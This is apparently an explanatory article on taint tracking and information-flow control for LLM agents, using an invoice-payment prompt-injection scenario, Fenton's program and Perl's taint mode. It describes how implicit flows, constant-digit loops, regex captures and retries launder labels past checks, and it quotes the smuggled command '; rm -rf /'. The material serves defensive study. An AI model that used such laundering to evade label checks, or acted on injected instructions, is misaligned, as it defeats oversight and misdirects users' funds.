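# How implicit flows and string operations defeat taint tracking in LLM agents

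## Labels, taint and the kinds of dependence they must follow

Taint tracking is a computer security technique for following data through a running program. The program labels every value that comes from an untrusted or sensitive source, such as a web form, a stranger's e-mail or a file of passwords. It passes the label on to whatever it computes from that value, and it refuses certain operations when a forbidden label reaches them. Security engineers have long used the technique on ordinary software, and researchers now apply it to LLM agents, programs in which a large language model (LLM) chooses the next action. If a value depends on labelled data but doesn't carry the label, the program allows the operation without warning.

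*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent as roughly the following loop. A program sends the model the conversation so far and a list of *tools*, which are functions the model may request, such as "read e-mail" or "send payment". The model returns either an answer for the user or a request to call a tool with particular arguments. If the model requests a call, the program makes it, appends the result to the conversation and repeats the loop.

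The user's instructions and the tool results therefore reach the model as one stream of text. In *indirect prompt injection*, an attacker who never talks to the model plants instructions in an e-mail, a web page or a hotel review that the agent will later read. If the model follows them, it acts with the user's permissions. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) traces the attack to a 2023 paper by Greshake and colleagues. Models have since become better at ignoring such instructions, but they are not immune. *Bounded Agents* (2026) cites a Gray Swan test with 272,000 attacks on 13 frontier models, in which every model obeyed some of the attacks, at rates from 0.5% to 8.5%. The main appeal of a label check is that it does not rely on the model recognising the attack.

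### Sources, sinks and joins

A *source* is a place where labelled data enters, and a *sink* is an operation, such as sending e-mail, that a label check guards. Propagation rules determine how labels spread between the two. *All You Ever Wanted to Know About Dynamic Taint Analysis*, by Schwartz, Avgerinos and Brumley, defines these rules for a small programming language in which every value is paired with its taint status. The result of an addition or multiplication is tainted if either operand is. If a program reads 20 from the user, doubles it and adds 5, the result, 45, is tainted, and any attempt to use it as the address of the next instruction halts the program.

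One bit of taint is enough for that job, but agents usually need two kinds of label. An *integrity* label records where a value came from, and hence who could have tampered with it. A *confidentiality* label records who may see it. In *Language-Based Information-Flow Security*, Sabelfeld and Myers (2003) credit Biba with observing that the two are symmetric, since confidentiality keeps information from flowing to the wrong destinations and integrity keeps it from flowing in from the wrong sources.

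The rule for combining labels goes back to Denning's 1976 paper *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, which describes a system by its security classes, a relation that defines which class may flow into which, and an operator that gives the class of a value computed from two others. Under mild assumptions these form a lattice, and the operator is the *join*, which gives the least restrictive class that is at least as restrictive as both inputs. If the result's class were any lower, a policy could allow `c := a + b` while forbidding `c := a`, and anyone could get around the ban by running the permitted statement with `b` set to zero.

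For agents, Costa and colleagues use a small lattice with two components. Integrity is trusted (T) or untrusted (U), with U the more restrictive; confidentiality is public (L, for low) or secret (H, for high), with H the more restrictive. Take a company's ledger, trusted and secret, and a supplier's web page, untrusted and public. A paragraph comparing the two gets the label

$$(T,H)\sqcup(U,L)=(T\sqcup U,\;H\sqcup L)=(U,H).$$

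The paragraph is now untrusted *and* secret, which neither input was. It may not decide a payment, and it may not leave the company.

Real deployments often replace "secret" with a list of permitted readers, and joining two labels then means intersecting their lists. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes an agent that reads one e-mail that Alex and Priya may read and another that Alex and Marco may read. Only Alex may read a reply based on both, so the agent may not send it to Marco on its own.

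Sometimes a user wants to allow an action that a label restricts. Deliberately removing a label is called *endorsement* for integrity labels and *declassification* for confidentiality labels. Any other step that leaves dependent data without its label, whether by accident or by design, is *laundering*.

### One invoice, four routes to the payment tool

Suppose a user tells an assistant to pay the invoice that a supplier has just e-mailed. The e-mail is a source and its contents are untrusted. The payment tool is a sink, and its rule is that the account number must be trusted. An attacker has broken into the supplier's mailbox and would like the money. Here are four ways in which the e-mail can determine where it goes:

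```
# copied
account = email.account

# inserted into a template
account = "{}{}".format("DE", email.number)

# selected by an if-statement
if "we have changed banks" in email.text:
    account = register.second_account
else:
    account = register.first_account

# restated by a model
account = model("Which account should we pay? " + email.text)

# and then, in every case
pay(account, amount)
```

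The copy is easy. The label travels with the value and the payment tool refuses it.

The template combines a trusted "DE" with an untrusted number, so the result should be untrusted. A simple tracker gets this right if the formatting function joins the two labels. Many string libraries don't do this, but that is a fixable defect in those libraries.

The if-statement copies nothing from the e-mail into `account`. Both candidate numbers come from the company's own supplier register and are trusted, so a simple tracker labels the result as trusted, and the payment goes to the account the attacker picked. A loop gives the attacker more than a choice between two registered accounts. It can compare each character of the e-mail with the digits 0 to 9 and, at every match, append its own constant digit to the account number. This rebuilds any number the attacker puts in the e-mail, using digits that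 never had a taint label.

The model's restatement is harder to label. The program sends the model a string and gets a new string back. The digits in the reply may be identical to those in the e-mail, but no operation in the program connects them, so a tracker with no rule for model calls will treat the reply as unlabelled data. The usual repair is to give the reply the *context label*, the join of the labels of everything the model had in its conversation. Costa and colleagues do this, and concede that it "may be overly conservative". Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, likewise treats any exposure to malicious text as tainting the whole output, including any tool calls the model might make.

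So a simple tracker follows the copy, and it follows the template if the string code passes the label along. It misses the if-statement, and it handles the model only if somebody has added a rule for it.

### Explicit and implicit flow

The difference between the copy and the if-statement has had a name for half a century. An *explicit flow* copies data, or computes with it, directly into another value. In an *implicit flow* the data decides which code runs, and affects a value that way. Denning and Denning (1977), in *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow*, show the second with two statements, where `x` is either 0 or 1:

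```
y := 1
if x = 0 then y := 0
```

At the end `y` equals `x`, although no statement ever copied `x` anywhere.

The standard remedy is a *program-counter label*, the label of the decisions that led to the code now running. When the assistant enters the if-statement, the tracker notes that an untrusted e-mail decided the branch, and joins "untrusted" into every value assigned inside it. The account number then arrives at the payment tool with the right label. This works as long as an assignment actually runs. In the example above, if `x` is 1, the program skips the assignment and the tracker has nothing to mark, yet `y` still gives `x` away. Schwartz and colleagues put the difficulty down to the method itself, since working out what a branch controls means reasoning about several paths and a run-time tracker follows only one. (Fenton's program, in the next section, turns this gap into a proof.)

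Implicit flows are common in agents. Whenever a model reads an e-mail and then decides which tool to call, the e-mail acts like the condition in an if-statement. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang et al., 2026), a survey that draws on the work of Denning and of Sabelfeld and Myers, makes a related distinction between evidence that supports a conclusion and events that merely influenced it. For instance, a false entry in an agent's memory can cause an action without supporting any conclusion. A tracker that searches a payment for words from the e-mail will miss this kind of influence.

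### Comparing two runs

What would it mean to catch every flow? The usual answer is *noninterference*: changing the labelled inputs changes nothing in the outputs that lack the label. The definition takes two runs. In the notation of Chong, in *Language-Based Security*, a program $c$ that turns starting state $\sigma$ into final state $\sigma'$ is noninterfering if, for every pair of runs,

$$\sigma_1 =_{Low} \sigma_2 \;\Rightarrow\; \sigma_1' =_{Low} \sigma_2'$$

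where $=_{Low}$ means that the two states agree on everything public. In other words, start the program twice with the same public data and different secrets, and an observer of the public results can't tell the runs apart. For integrity, hold the trusted data fixed and vary the untrusted data instead.

To apply the test to the invoice, we run the assistant twice, with two e-mails that differ in the part that matters, and compare the payments. In all four versions of the code, the two runs can send the money to different accounts. All four are therefore violations if the tracker has left the account number marked as trusted, whether the e-mail influenced it through a copy, a branch or a neural network.

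The definition is also stricter than people want. The user asked the assistant to pay the account in the e-mail, so the payment has to depend on the e-mail. Ma and colleagues call such requests "param-open", meaning that the user names the action and leaves its details to be read from the content. They add that typical use falls into the less precisely specified categories. A system that strictly enforced noninterference would have to refuse these requests or rely on an endorsement, such as a phone call to the supplier to confirm the account number.

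Many practical systems provide only a weaker guarantee than noninterference, such as *explicit secrecy*, which covers explicit flows of secrets but not what an observer could learn from which path the program takes. Costa and colleagues prove that their tracker provides explicit secrecy. They argue that once an agent has used a tool that may read secrets, full noninterference would come close to banning any tool that may write public data.

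### Two kinds of error, and the trade between them

*Under-tainting* occurs when a value depends on labelled data but doesn't carry the label. *Over-tainting*, or *label creep*, occurs when labels spread to values that don't depend on the labelled data. A standard example of over-tainting is `a xor a`, which machine code often uses to set a register to zero. The result is always zero, but a naive tracker marks it as tainted whenever `a` was.

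Under-tainting is clearly worse for security than over-tainting. If a payment is over-tainted, it gets blocked, the user complains, and somebody fixes the rule, whereas an under-tainted payment goes through. Attackers can also look for these misses, because they write the input and can keep trying until some phrasing gets through unlabelled. But over-tainting can weaken security too. Systems that block too much tend to ask a human for approval instead, and Costa and colleagues warn that people who see too many such requests stop reading them.

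Fixing one error tends to cause the other. Schwartz and colleagues describe a program that uses a number from the user to look up an entry in a table, then jumps to the address it finds there. The entry itself is untainted, so a simple tracker allows the jump even though the attacker chose the destination, as with the two registered bank accounts. Tainting anything fetched with a tainted index would catch this. But `tcpdump`, a widely used program for inspecting network traffic, legitimately picks its printing routine this way, from the first byte of each packet, so the stricter rule would raise an alarm on every non-trivial run.

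Taint-tracking systems in general seem to be inaccurate. Yan and Yin surveyed a number of them and found that every one either missed real flows or reported false ones. Program-counter labels have the same problem. A tracker can leave the label raised for the rest of the run to avoid missing flows through branches not taken, but Sabelfeld and Myers judge the resulting label creep too restrictive for general use.

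In an agent, label creep can happen almost immediately. Once the supplier's e-mail enters the conversation, the context is labelled untrusted, and so is every later tool call, even a rent payment to an account the user typed in. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls this "label explosion" and treats separating flows inside a model as an open research problem.

### The dual-LLM pattern and AgentDojo

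One way to limit the creep is to keep untrusted text away from the model that makes decisions. In the *dual-LLM pattern*, which Willison proposed in April 2023, a privileged model plans and calls tools without seeing untrusted data, while a quarantined model reads that data and has no tools. The planner refers to the results only by variable name, so it can request a payment to `$VAR1` without reading its contents. An injection in an e-mail can't add a tool call to the plan, but it can still corrupt the contents of `$VAR1`, so the variable needs a label and the payment tool has to check that label.

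Most of the agent defences in the following sections report results on *AgentDojo*, a benchmark by Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024). It pairs ordinary user tasks, such as paying a bill from a text file, with attackers' goals in simulated workspace, Slack, travel and banking environments. It checks the final state of the environment with ordinary code instead of asking another model to judge. Its main measures are the share of tasks the agent completes, with and without an attack, and the share of attacks that succeed. The 2024 version had 97 user tasks and 629 attack cases. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) reports over 900 pairings.

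Ma and colleagues found that AgentDojo's fixed, hand-written attacks often make defences look much stronger than they are against an attacker who adapts. A further problem for taint tracking is that the benchmark counts successful attacks, not lost labels. When *aiAuthZ* (2026) ran a standard AgentDojo attack on two current models in the banking environment, with 20 pairings per condition, the attack never succeeded even without a defence, so a tracker that dropped every label would also have received a perfect score.

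## Fenton's program: how a branch that never runs leaks a secret

Denning and Denning's two-statement example leaks `x` through an assignment that doesn't run, but it fools a tracker only half the time. If `x` is 0, the assignment does run, and `y` gets the right label. In 1974 J. S. Fenton published a program that chains two such branches together, so that the result carries the wrong label whatever the secret is. Denning discussed it two years later. Austin and Flanagan (2010), in *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis*, use a version with the truth values inverted, which is a little easier to read. Here `x` is secret and everything else starts out public:

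```
y = true
z = true
if x: y = false
if y: z = false
return z
```

Suppose a tracker runs this program and marks a variable as secret whenever the program assigns to it inside a branch that depends on a secret. The two possible runs go as follows.

| Statement | Run with `x` true | Run with `x` false |
|---|---|---|
| `y = true`, `z = true` | both true, public | both true, public |
| `if x: y = false` | assignment runs; `y` is false, secret | assignment doesn't run; `y` is still true, public |
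| `if y: z = false` | assignment doesn't run; `z` is still true, public | assignment runs; `z` is false, public |
| `return z` | true, public | false, public |

So `z` always ends up equal to `x`, and its label always says "public". The program could now e-mail it to anyone.

In the right-hand column of the table, the program tests `y`, which is labeled public, so the tracker doesn't mark `z`. The mistake happens one row earlier, where `y` stays true *because* `x` is false but its label doesn't reflect that. Austin and Flanagan call `y` "partially leaked", since its label is wrong in only one of the two runs, and `z` "totally leaked".

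The trick works just as well against integrity tracking. If `x` is one bit of the account number in the attacker's e-mail, the program returns a copy of that bit labelled as trusted.

### What the program-counter label does and doesn't do

The tracker in the table already has a program-counter label. Without one, it would get even the secret `y` in the left-hand column wrong.

The idea comes from Fenton's Data Mark Machine, an abstract computer with a security tag on every memory cell. When a program enters a conditional, the machine pushes the current program-counter label onto a stack and replaces it with the join of that label and the label of the condition. When the program leaves the conditional, the machine pops the stack and gets the old label back. If labels can change during the run, an assignment of some function of $a_1,\dots,a_n$ to $b$ sets

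$$\mathrm{label}(b) := \mathrm{label}(a_1)\sqcup\dots\sqcup\mathrm{label}(a_n)\sqcup pc.$$

This rule takes effect only at an assignment. If `x` is false, the machine still raises $pc$ to secret when it tests `x`, but it executes no assignment before it leaves the conditional and lowers $pc$ again. By the time it tests `y`, nothing in its state records that it branched on `x`.

Fenton's machine avoided this leak because it fixed every variable's label in advance and checked assignments instead of updating labels. If `y` is permanently public, the machine skips the assignment `y = false` inside the branch on `x`. Then `y` is true in both runs, and an observer learns nothing from it. Fenton proved that with fixed labels, checking only the assignments that run is enough.

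However, error messages can leak the secret. Denning points out that a program could deliberately commit a number of violations equal to the secret's value, and the program's owner could then read that value from the log of aborted operations. One solution is to skip forbidden operations without logging them, but this makes programs hard to debug.

Fixed labels also work poorly for agents. A variable called `result` may hold a public web page at one step and a salary list at the next, and if a model has just written the code, nobody has declared what any variable may contain. Most agent trackers therefore let a variable's label change with the data it holds, which is the behavior that lets Fenton's program leak its secret.

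Raising the program-counter label and never lowering it catches Fenton's program within a single run, provided that the tracker also applies the label to the program's output. Besides label creep, Denning found another problem with this approach. Suppose one process runs the test on `x` and a second process runs the test on `y`, which is in storage they share. The first process's raised label disappears when that process ends. If `x` was false, the first process never touched `y`, so the second process starts with a clean label and `y` still has a clean label too, even though its value reveals `x`. Denning found this flaw in two security systems of the period, ADEPT-50 and Rotenberg's Privacy Restriction Processor. An agent that writes a note to its memory file only under some condition, and reads the file in a later session, has the same structure.

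### A monitor that watches one run can't fix this

It would be nice if a cleverer update rule solved the problem, but Russo and Sabelfeld, in *Dynamic vs. Static Flow-Sensitive Security Analysis*, proved that none exists. They call a monitor purely dynamic if it looks neither ahead, at instructions still to come, nor aside, at the branch that the program didn't take. No monitor of this kind can stop every leak and also let through, unmodified, every program that a standard static analysis certifies as safe. (The analysis they have in mind also lets a variable's label change from line to line.)

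Fenton's program shows why. Replacing only `y = false` with an instruction that does nothing makes the program return false whatever `x` is. Replacing only `z = false` makes it always return true. Both edited programs are harmless and the static analysis accepts them, so the monitor has to accept them too.

If `x` is false, the original program executes exactly the same instructions as the version without `y = false`. If `x` is true, it executes the same instructions as the version without `z = false`. Both of those versions are harmless, and a monitor that can't inspect the untaken branch can't distinguish the original from them. It therefore has to let the original finish in both cases, and the different results reveal `x`.

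Any repair must therefore look at code that didn't run, run the program more than once, or put up with interfering in some harmless programs. This is what Fenton's program returns under each of the repairs below:

| Repair | `x` true | `x` false |
|---|---|---|
| Label whatever either branch could assign | true, secret | false, secret |
| Undo the branch's assignments on leaving it | false, public | false, public |
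| No-sensitive-upgrade | stops at `y = false` | false, public |
| Permissive upgrade | stops at `if y` | false, public |
| Secure multi-execution or faceted values | false for the public, true for those cleared to see `x` | false for everyone |

### Analysing the branch not taken

A static analysis examines the whole program before it runs. In Denning's version, a compiler lists every variable that any branch of a conditional assigns, and checks that the condition's label may flow into all of them. If `x` is secret and `y` is public, the line `if x: y = false` fails the check. Because the check happens before the program runs, it leaves no error log to exploit and adds no run-time overhead.

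For labels that change during the run, Denning combined the two approaches. The compiler works out which variables a branch might assign and, at the end of the conditional, adds an instruction that joins the program-counter label into their labels. In Fenton's program, `y` then becomes secret after the test on `x`, whether or not the assignment ran. The test on `y` is therefore secret in both runs, so `z` becomes secret at the end of it.

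To do this, the compiler has to determine what a branch might assign. That is easy if the branch contains `y = false`, but much harder if it calls a function that the program picks at run time or changes an object that several variables share. Austin and Flanagan rule out type-based static analysis for browser programs because JavaScript is dynamically typed, and Python, in which agents often write their code, is too. An analysis that can't determine what a branch assigns has to label everything the branch might assign, including data that doesn't need the label, which causes label creep.

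Static checkers also reject programs that leak nothing. Many static analyses reject Austin and Flanagan's example, which sets `y` to true if a secret is true and then returns the constant `true` without using `y`.

The third difficulty is annotation, since somebody has to write down which data is secret. This now takes much less work. Ching, Zhou and Zhang (2026) built *Filament*, a checker with a compile-time program-counter label, as an ordinary Rust library that needs no changes to the compiler. They used it to rewrite five applications, four of which came from an earlier Rust library called Cocoon, and removed 12 declassifications and unchecked operations that Cocoon's versions had contained. But Rust programmers already write down types for the compiler, so Filament has a much better starting point than a tool for model-written Python would.

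Russo and Sabelfeld suggest a hybrid monitor, which watches the program run and uses static analysis where needed. They show that such monitors can be secure and accept more programs than the static analysis alone. If the offending code is in an untaken branch of a conditional that the program reaches only for certain inputs, a hybrid monitor can allow the runs that never reach that conditional.

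Denning also describes an older proposal, by Fenton and by Gat and Saal, that needs no analysis. If a branch raises a variable's label, the machine restores the variable's old value and label when it leaves the branch. In Fenton's program, this resets `y` to true, so the program always returns false. This stops the leak but changes what the program does. Under this rule, a branch on a secret can use public variables only for temporary values.

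### Stopping the run

Under the *no-sensitive-upgrade* rule, the monitor stops the run if the program tries to assign to a currently public variable inside a branch that depends on a secret. This blocks the assignment that makes `y`'s label depend on the secret. Austin and Flanagan (2009), in *Efficient purely-dynamic information flow analysis*, used a run-time check of this kind to guarantee noninterference for a language like JavaScript without static analysis.

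When `x` is true, Fenton's program stops at `y = false`. It reaches the end only when `x` is false, so every answer it outputs is the same.

No-sensitive-upgrade also stops harmless programs. For example, a program might set `y` to false inside a branch on a secret, then unconditionally set it back to true and return it. The program should always return true, which reveals nothing, but under no-sensitive-upgrade it stops inside the branch whenever the secret is true.

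Austin and Flanagan's *permissive-upgrade* rule lets that program finish. It adds a third label, P, for partially leaked data, which contains secret information but might be marked public in another run. In Fenton's program with `x` true, the rule allows the assignment, and `y` becomes false with label P. The monitor stops the run only if the program then does something sensitive with `y`, such as branching on it. Fenton's program branches on `y` in the next line, so the monitor still stops it. In the harmless program, the final assignment replaces the P value with a public one, and the run continues.

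A programmer can avoid the stop by adding an annotation that marks `y` as secret just before the test. This is safe because the annotation takes effect in both runs, including the one where `y` had kept its public label. However, `z` now has the same problem. It gets label P when `x` is false, because the program assigns to it inside what is now a secret branch, but keeps its public label when `x` is true. If the program later branches on `z`, it needs another annotation there.

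Finding all these places by hand would be tedious, so Austin and Flanagan let the runtime find them. During a trial period, the runtime adds an annotation wherever a run would have got stuck, then lets the run continue. The program is finite, so the runtime must eventually run out of places to annotate, and the developer can then release the annotated version with the rule switched on. Until then, there is no guarantee against leaks. This approach suits a web application with many users, but it works poorly for a program that a model writes for a single request, because that program usually runs only once.

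### Running the program more than once

Noninterference compares two runs of a program, and *secure multi-execution* enforces it by running the program once for each label. The public run receives a default in place of the secret, say `x` = false, and only this run may write to public outputs. The secret run receives the real `x` and may write only to secret outputs. The public output can't depend on `x`, whichever branches the program takes, because the run that produced it never received the real value.

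*Faceted values* get a similar effect within one run. A variable that depends on a secret holds a pair $\langle s \mid p\rangle$, where $s$ is the value for people who may know the secret and $p$ is the value for everyone else. When the program branches on such a pair and the two halves disagree, the interpreter executes the code for both. If `x` is true and the default is false, Fenton's program computes

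$$x=\langle \mathrm{true}\mid \mathrm{false}\rangle,\quad y=\langle \mathrm{false}\mid \mathrm{true}\rangle,\quad z=\langle \mathrm{true}\mid \mathrm{false}\rangle.$$

If `x` is false, both halves of `z` are false. The public half is the same either way.

Neither technique needs to reject programs. The public gets the correct answer from a program that was already safe, but silently gets a wrong one from a leaky program. Both techniques also take extra computation. With $n$ independent secrets, different readers may be cleared for any subset of them, so there can be up to $2^n$ versions of a value to keep.

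Using multiple runs creates further problems for agents. If the runs differ before a model call, the agent has to pay for that call twice. It must send an e-mail or move money only once, so the runtime needs a rule for which run does it. In the invoice example, the trusted run would receive a default e-mail with no account number instead of the supplier's e-mail, so the payment would be secure but would not reach the supplier.

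### One bit per run

The no-sensitive-upgrade rule doesn't fully enforce noninterference. If Fenton's program prints "false", the observer knows that `x` was false. If it prints nothing because the monitor stopped it, the observer can infer that `x` was true.

The guarantee that the rule does deliver is *termination-insensitive noninterference*, which compares only runs that finish:

$$\sigma_1 =_{Low} \sigma_2 \;\text{ and both runs terminate} \;\Rightarrow\; \sigma_1' =_{Low} \sigma_2'.$$

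A secret may influence whether the program finishes, but not which public result it gives if it does. Most static checkers settle for the same guarantee, since the alternative is to prove that programs always finish or to ban loops that depend on secrets. (Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, extend the definition to programs that sample random replies from a language model.)

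The usual excuse for this gap is that it leaks at most one bit per run. If the program prints as it goes along, that is wrong, as Askarov, Hunt and colleagues, in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit*, showed in 2008 with a program like this one:

```
for i in range(2**32):
    print(i)                 # a public output
    if i == secret:
        while true: pass     # hang
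```

The last number printed is the secret. Yet well-known checkers for Java, Caml and Ada accept programs of this form, because the printing depends only on `i` and the branch on the secret assigns nothing.

In a timed test of the attack, the program wrote each number to shared memory to reduce the overhead of printing, and a second process watched for the number to stop changing. On a 3 GHz machine, this leaked a 32-bit secret in under six seconds. At the same rate, a credit card number (about 50 bits) would take roughly 18 and a half days, and a 128-bit encryption key would take too long to be practical.

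Askarov and colleagues proved that no program satisfying the definition can do fundamentally better. At each step, the program either prints the same value it would print for any secret, or it hangs, so a step can single out at most one candidate. To be certain of learning an $N$-bit secret, the attacker must be prepared to watch at least $2^N-1$ steps. If all secrets are equally likely, watching $t$ steps improves the chance of guessing correctly by at most $t/2^N$.

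This result is reassuring for long keys only if the attacker observes a single run, as the proof assumes. An attacker who can repeat runs can execute Fenton's program under no-sensitive-upgrade with `x` as the first bit of the key, note whether it finishes, and then do the same for each remaining bit. Recovering a 128-bit key this way takes 128 short runs, whereas the counting program would need around $2^{128}$ steps.

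An attacker may not be able to rerun ordinary software at will, but agent frameworks often rerun failed programs, usually from a loop outside the tracked code. Garby and colleagues found both Fenton's missed assignment and an untracked retry loop in the interpreter of CaMeL, a defence in which agents act by running model-written code. A program that can start many processes doesn't need retries, since it can give each process one bit to test. Capping the number of attempts limits the leak to about one bit per attempt, as long as each attempt produces no output before it ends.

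### Implicit flows in ordinary software

Implicit flows may not matter much in programs that weren't written to leak data. The taint modes of Perl and Ruby have found many real bugs without tracking them, while few people have used the compilers that do track them to enforce noninterference.

In *Implicit Flows*, King, Hicks and colleagues (2008) tried to find out why. They applied the standard noninterference analysis to implementations of authentication and cryptographic functions, then sorted the true alarms from the false ones. The analysis found many real implicit flows, but it also raised a great many false alarms. Most of these came from its cautious treatment of unchecked exceptions, such as the error Java raises when a program uses a null pointer.

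It isn't hard to see how exceptions do this. Suppose a program looks up a user's record with a secret key and then reads a field of the record:

```
record = table.lookup(secret_key)
n = record.length
log("lookup finished")
```

If the record is null, the second line fails and the program never writes to the log. So in theory, the log entry depends on the secret. The programmer may know that the record always exists, but the analysis lacks that information, so it has to treat everything after the second line as if it were inside a branch on the secret. Almost any line that uses an object can fail in this way.

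Many of the real flows are also harmless. A login function has to reveal whether a password was right, and its answer depends on the stored password through a branch. This is an implicit flow, so a checker is correct to report it, but the developer still has to write a declassification to suppress the report.

One way to separate the login function from a real leak is to count the bits of the secret that each gives away. A failed login gives away very little about a good password, whereas a loop that copies the password through branches gives away all of it. McCamant and Ernst (2008), in *Quantitative information flow as network flow capacity*, treat a program as a network of pipes and compute how many bits of secret information could have reached the output in the runs they observed, including through branches. They tried this on five real programs, three of them with more than 250,000 lines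 of code, and found a previously unknown bug that violated one of the policies they checked.

Bit counts are less useful for integrity. In the invoice example, the attacker needs only one bit to pick the second of the supplier's two registered accounts, so a rule that ignores small flows would allow the attack and the company would lose the whole payment.

### Attackers who write code and attackers who write e-mails

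People disagree about implicit flows largely because they have different attackers in mind. *Implicit flows in malicious and nonmalicious code* (2009) describes two extremes in the literature. One is to track all implicit flows despite the false alarms. The other is to ignore these flows, which gives weak guarantees or none. The paper argues that the right choice depends on whether the code itself is hostile.

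Ignoring implicit flows can be reasonable if the attacker supplies only data. Bello and Russo (2012), in *Towards a Taint Mode for Cloud Computing Web Applications*, built a taint tracker that follows only explicit flows. It is meant to catch a programmer who forgets to clean up a visitor's text before putting it on a web page. The programmer isn't trying to evade the tracker, and the visitor can't change the program. The text would lose its label only if the program rebuilt it character by character through branches, which people seldom do by accident, though some parsers and format converters come close.

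If the attacker writes the code, a tracker of this kind is close to useless, and Bello and Russo say taint analysis isn't meant for this case. Malware that expects a taint tracker can get past it with simple tricks. For example, the loop that rebuilt an account number from constant digits can make an untainted copy of any other text in the same way. Bay and Askarov note in *Reconciling progress-insensitive noninterference and declassification* that untrusted code is also a reason to close the termination channel, while a weaker guarantee may do for code that people trust not to abuse it.

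When an agent runs code that a model has written, which of these attackers it faces depends on what the model read before writing the code.

In the dual-LLM pattern, the planning model sees only the user's request, so the attacker supplies only data. The model has no reason to write Fenton's program, but it may well write `if "we have changed banks" in email.text`, which is a natural way to handle a supplier with two accounts. The attacker can't add a branch but can decide which way an existing one goes. Requests such as "pay this invoice" are common and models tend to answer them in similar ways, so an attacker can probably guess which branches the program will contain. A tracker for this setting doesn't need to be very strict about elaborate laundering loops, but it must handle a plain branch that chooses between trusted values, which the web tracker could ignore.

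But if the model reads the supplier's e-mail before writing the code, an attacker can use the e-mail to ask for any program, including Fenton's, which current models can easily write. The model might refuse, but a label check was supposed to work even if it doesn't.

Garby and colleagues adopt a blunt solution for integrity. The code starts with its program-counter label set to the context label of the model that wrote it. If the model has read an untrusted e-mail, everything its code computes is untrusted, however the code branches. This does not protect secrets that the program looks up later, such as an account balance. If the e-mail was public, the code starts with a public confidentiality label and can use Fenton's program to leak the balance, unless the tracker has one of the repairs.

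Retries can push an agent from the safer situation towards the riskier one. Suppose the planner has seen nothing untrusted, and the payment tool rejects its program because the account number came from an e-mail. The framework returns the error to the model and prompts it for a corrected version. The model might then write code that searches the supplier register for a matching number and pays that entry. A tracker that ignores branches will accept this, because the number now comes from the register. The check may also be good practice, since a careful clerk would do the same. It counts as endorsement if the company approved it in advance, and as laundering if the model devised it to get past the rejection.

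## String taint in Perl, Python and document converters

Programs also lose taint labels in ordinary text handling, often with no branch involved. Agents routinely paste e-mails into prompts, cut account numbers out of replies and convert tool results to JSON, and any of these steps can return text that looks the same but has no label. Scripting languages had this problem long before agents did.

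### Perl's taint mode

*A Taint Mode for Python via a Library* (Conti and Russo, 2012) credits Perl as the first scripting language to offer taint tracking as an interpreter mode. In this mode, Perl marks all data from outside the program as tainted, including command-line arguments, environment variables and file contents. It stops with a fatal error if tainted data reaches a command that starts a shell or changes files, directories or processes.

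If any part of an expression is tainted, Perl may treat the whole expression as tainted, even the parts that the tainted data can't affect. In an example from Perl's manual, a line mentions a tainted variable and then, after a comma, tries to run the fixed command `true`. Perl blocks the command, and the manual's comment on the line is "Insecure (although it isn't really)".

The reason is speed. In *Taint bug with multiple backticks in ref consturctors* (p5pRT, 2003), a user complained that Perl wouldn't run this line:

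```perl
my $vars = [`echo "FOO"`, `echo "BAR"`];
```

Backticks in Perl run a shell command and return its output, which is tainted. Perl keeps one taint flag for the whole expression, so if a list contains two backtick commands, the output of the first raises the flag and Perl refuses to run the second, even though its text is a constant. If the program instead stores the first output in a variable and puts that variable in the list, the second command runs. Mike Guy, who patched the manual in response, called this "Feature, not a bug" and explained that the outcome depends on the order in which Perl evaluates the expression. Refusing to run the constant command is a false positive, although the SEI, a software engineering institute at Carnegie Mellon University, writes that taint mode produces none.

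### The ternary exemption

Perl makes an exception for the ternary operator, which picks one of two values depending on a condition:

```perl
$result = $tainted_value ? "Untainted" : "Also untainted";
```

Here `$result` is clean. According to the manual, the line is effectively an `if` statement that assigns one of two constants, so "it doesn't make sense for $result to be tainted".

The two forms are equivalent, and Perl leaves `$result` clean in both, so the exemption is consistent with how Perl treats `if`. But `$result` still depends on the tainted value. In the two-run test, changing `$tainted_value` from 1 to 0 also changes `$result`.

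The exemption makes more sense given that taint mode is mainly meant to stop outsiders from smuggling commands into a shell. If the programmer wrote both strings, an outsider who picks between them can't add `; rm -rf /` to either. But if the strings are bank account numbers, an attacker only needs to pick between them. The protection against smuggled commands also fails if the program makes enough choices, since a loop of ternaries can rebuild any text from constants.

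Perl also exempts method names held in variables from taint checks, so a program can call `$obj->$method(@args)` even if `$method` is tainted. The manual warns that outsiders may then be able to call functions such as `POSIX::system`, which runs arbitrary commands. An agent framework that looks up a tool by the name in the model's reply has the same structure.

### Captures and hash keys

Sometimes a program has checked its input and needs to clear the taint. Perl's usual method is a regular expression. Any text that the program captures with parentheses in the pattern comes out clean:

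```perl
if ($email =~ /account: (\w+)/) {
    $account = $1;              # clean
}

$seen{$_} = 1 for @addresses;
@unique = keys %seen;           # clean
```

The Perl manual's example accepts only letters, digits, underscores and a few punctuation marks, then uses the captured copy. This is endorsement, and its safety depends on the pattern. The pattern `.+` lets almost everything through, and Perl doesn't check whether a pattern is too permissive. The SEI points out that the captured text can be identical to the tainted original and still count as clean.

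The trouble is that programmers also use captures simply to find things. The first snippet above looks for an account number in an e-mail, and its author may never have thought about taint. The number comes out clean anyway. Perl can't tell a security check from a search, so it treats every capture as an endorsement. (There is one careful exception. Under `use locale`, settings from outside the program decide which characters `\w` matches, so Perl keeps the taint.)

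The second snippet is a common way to remove duplicates from a list. It puts each address into a hash, Perl's lookup table, and reads back the keys. Perl attaches taint to scalar values and never to hash keys, so the addresses come back untainted. The manual lists this as a way to untaint data on purpose, but a programmer who only wants to send each person one e-mail does it by accident.

Even a deliberate check may not suit the way the text is later used. Text that is safe in a web address may be unsafe in a web page, but Perl has only one kind of taint, so text cleaned for one purpose is marked as untainted for all of them. The SEI recommends against relying on taint mode for scripts that interact with the web, partly for this reason.

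### A Python string that carries a label

Python has no taint mode, but it allows programmers to extend its string class. This small class gives each string a label:

```python
def join_labels(*parts):
    labels = [getattr(p, "label", "trusted") for p in parts]
    return "untrusted" if "untrusted" in labels else "trusted"

class Labelled(str):
    def __new__(cls, text, label):
        s = str.__new__(cls, text)
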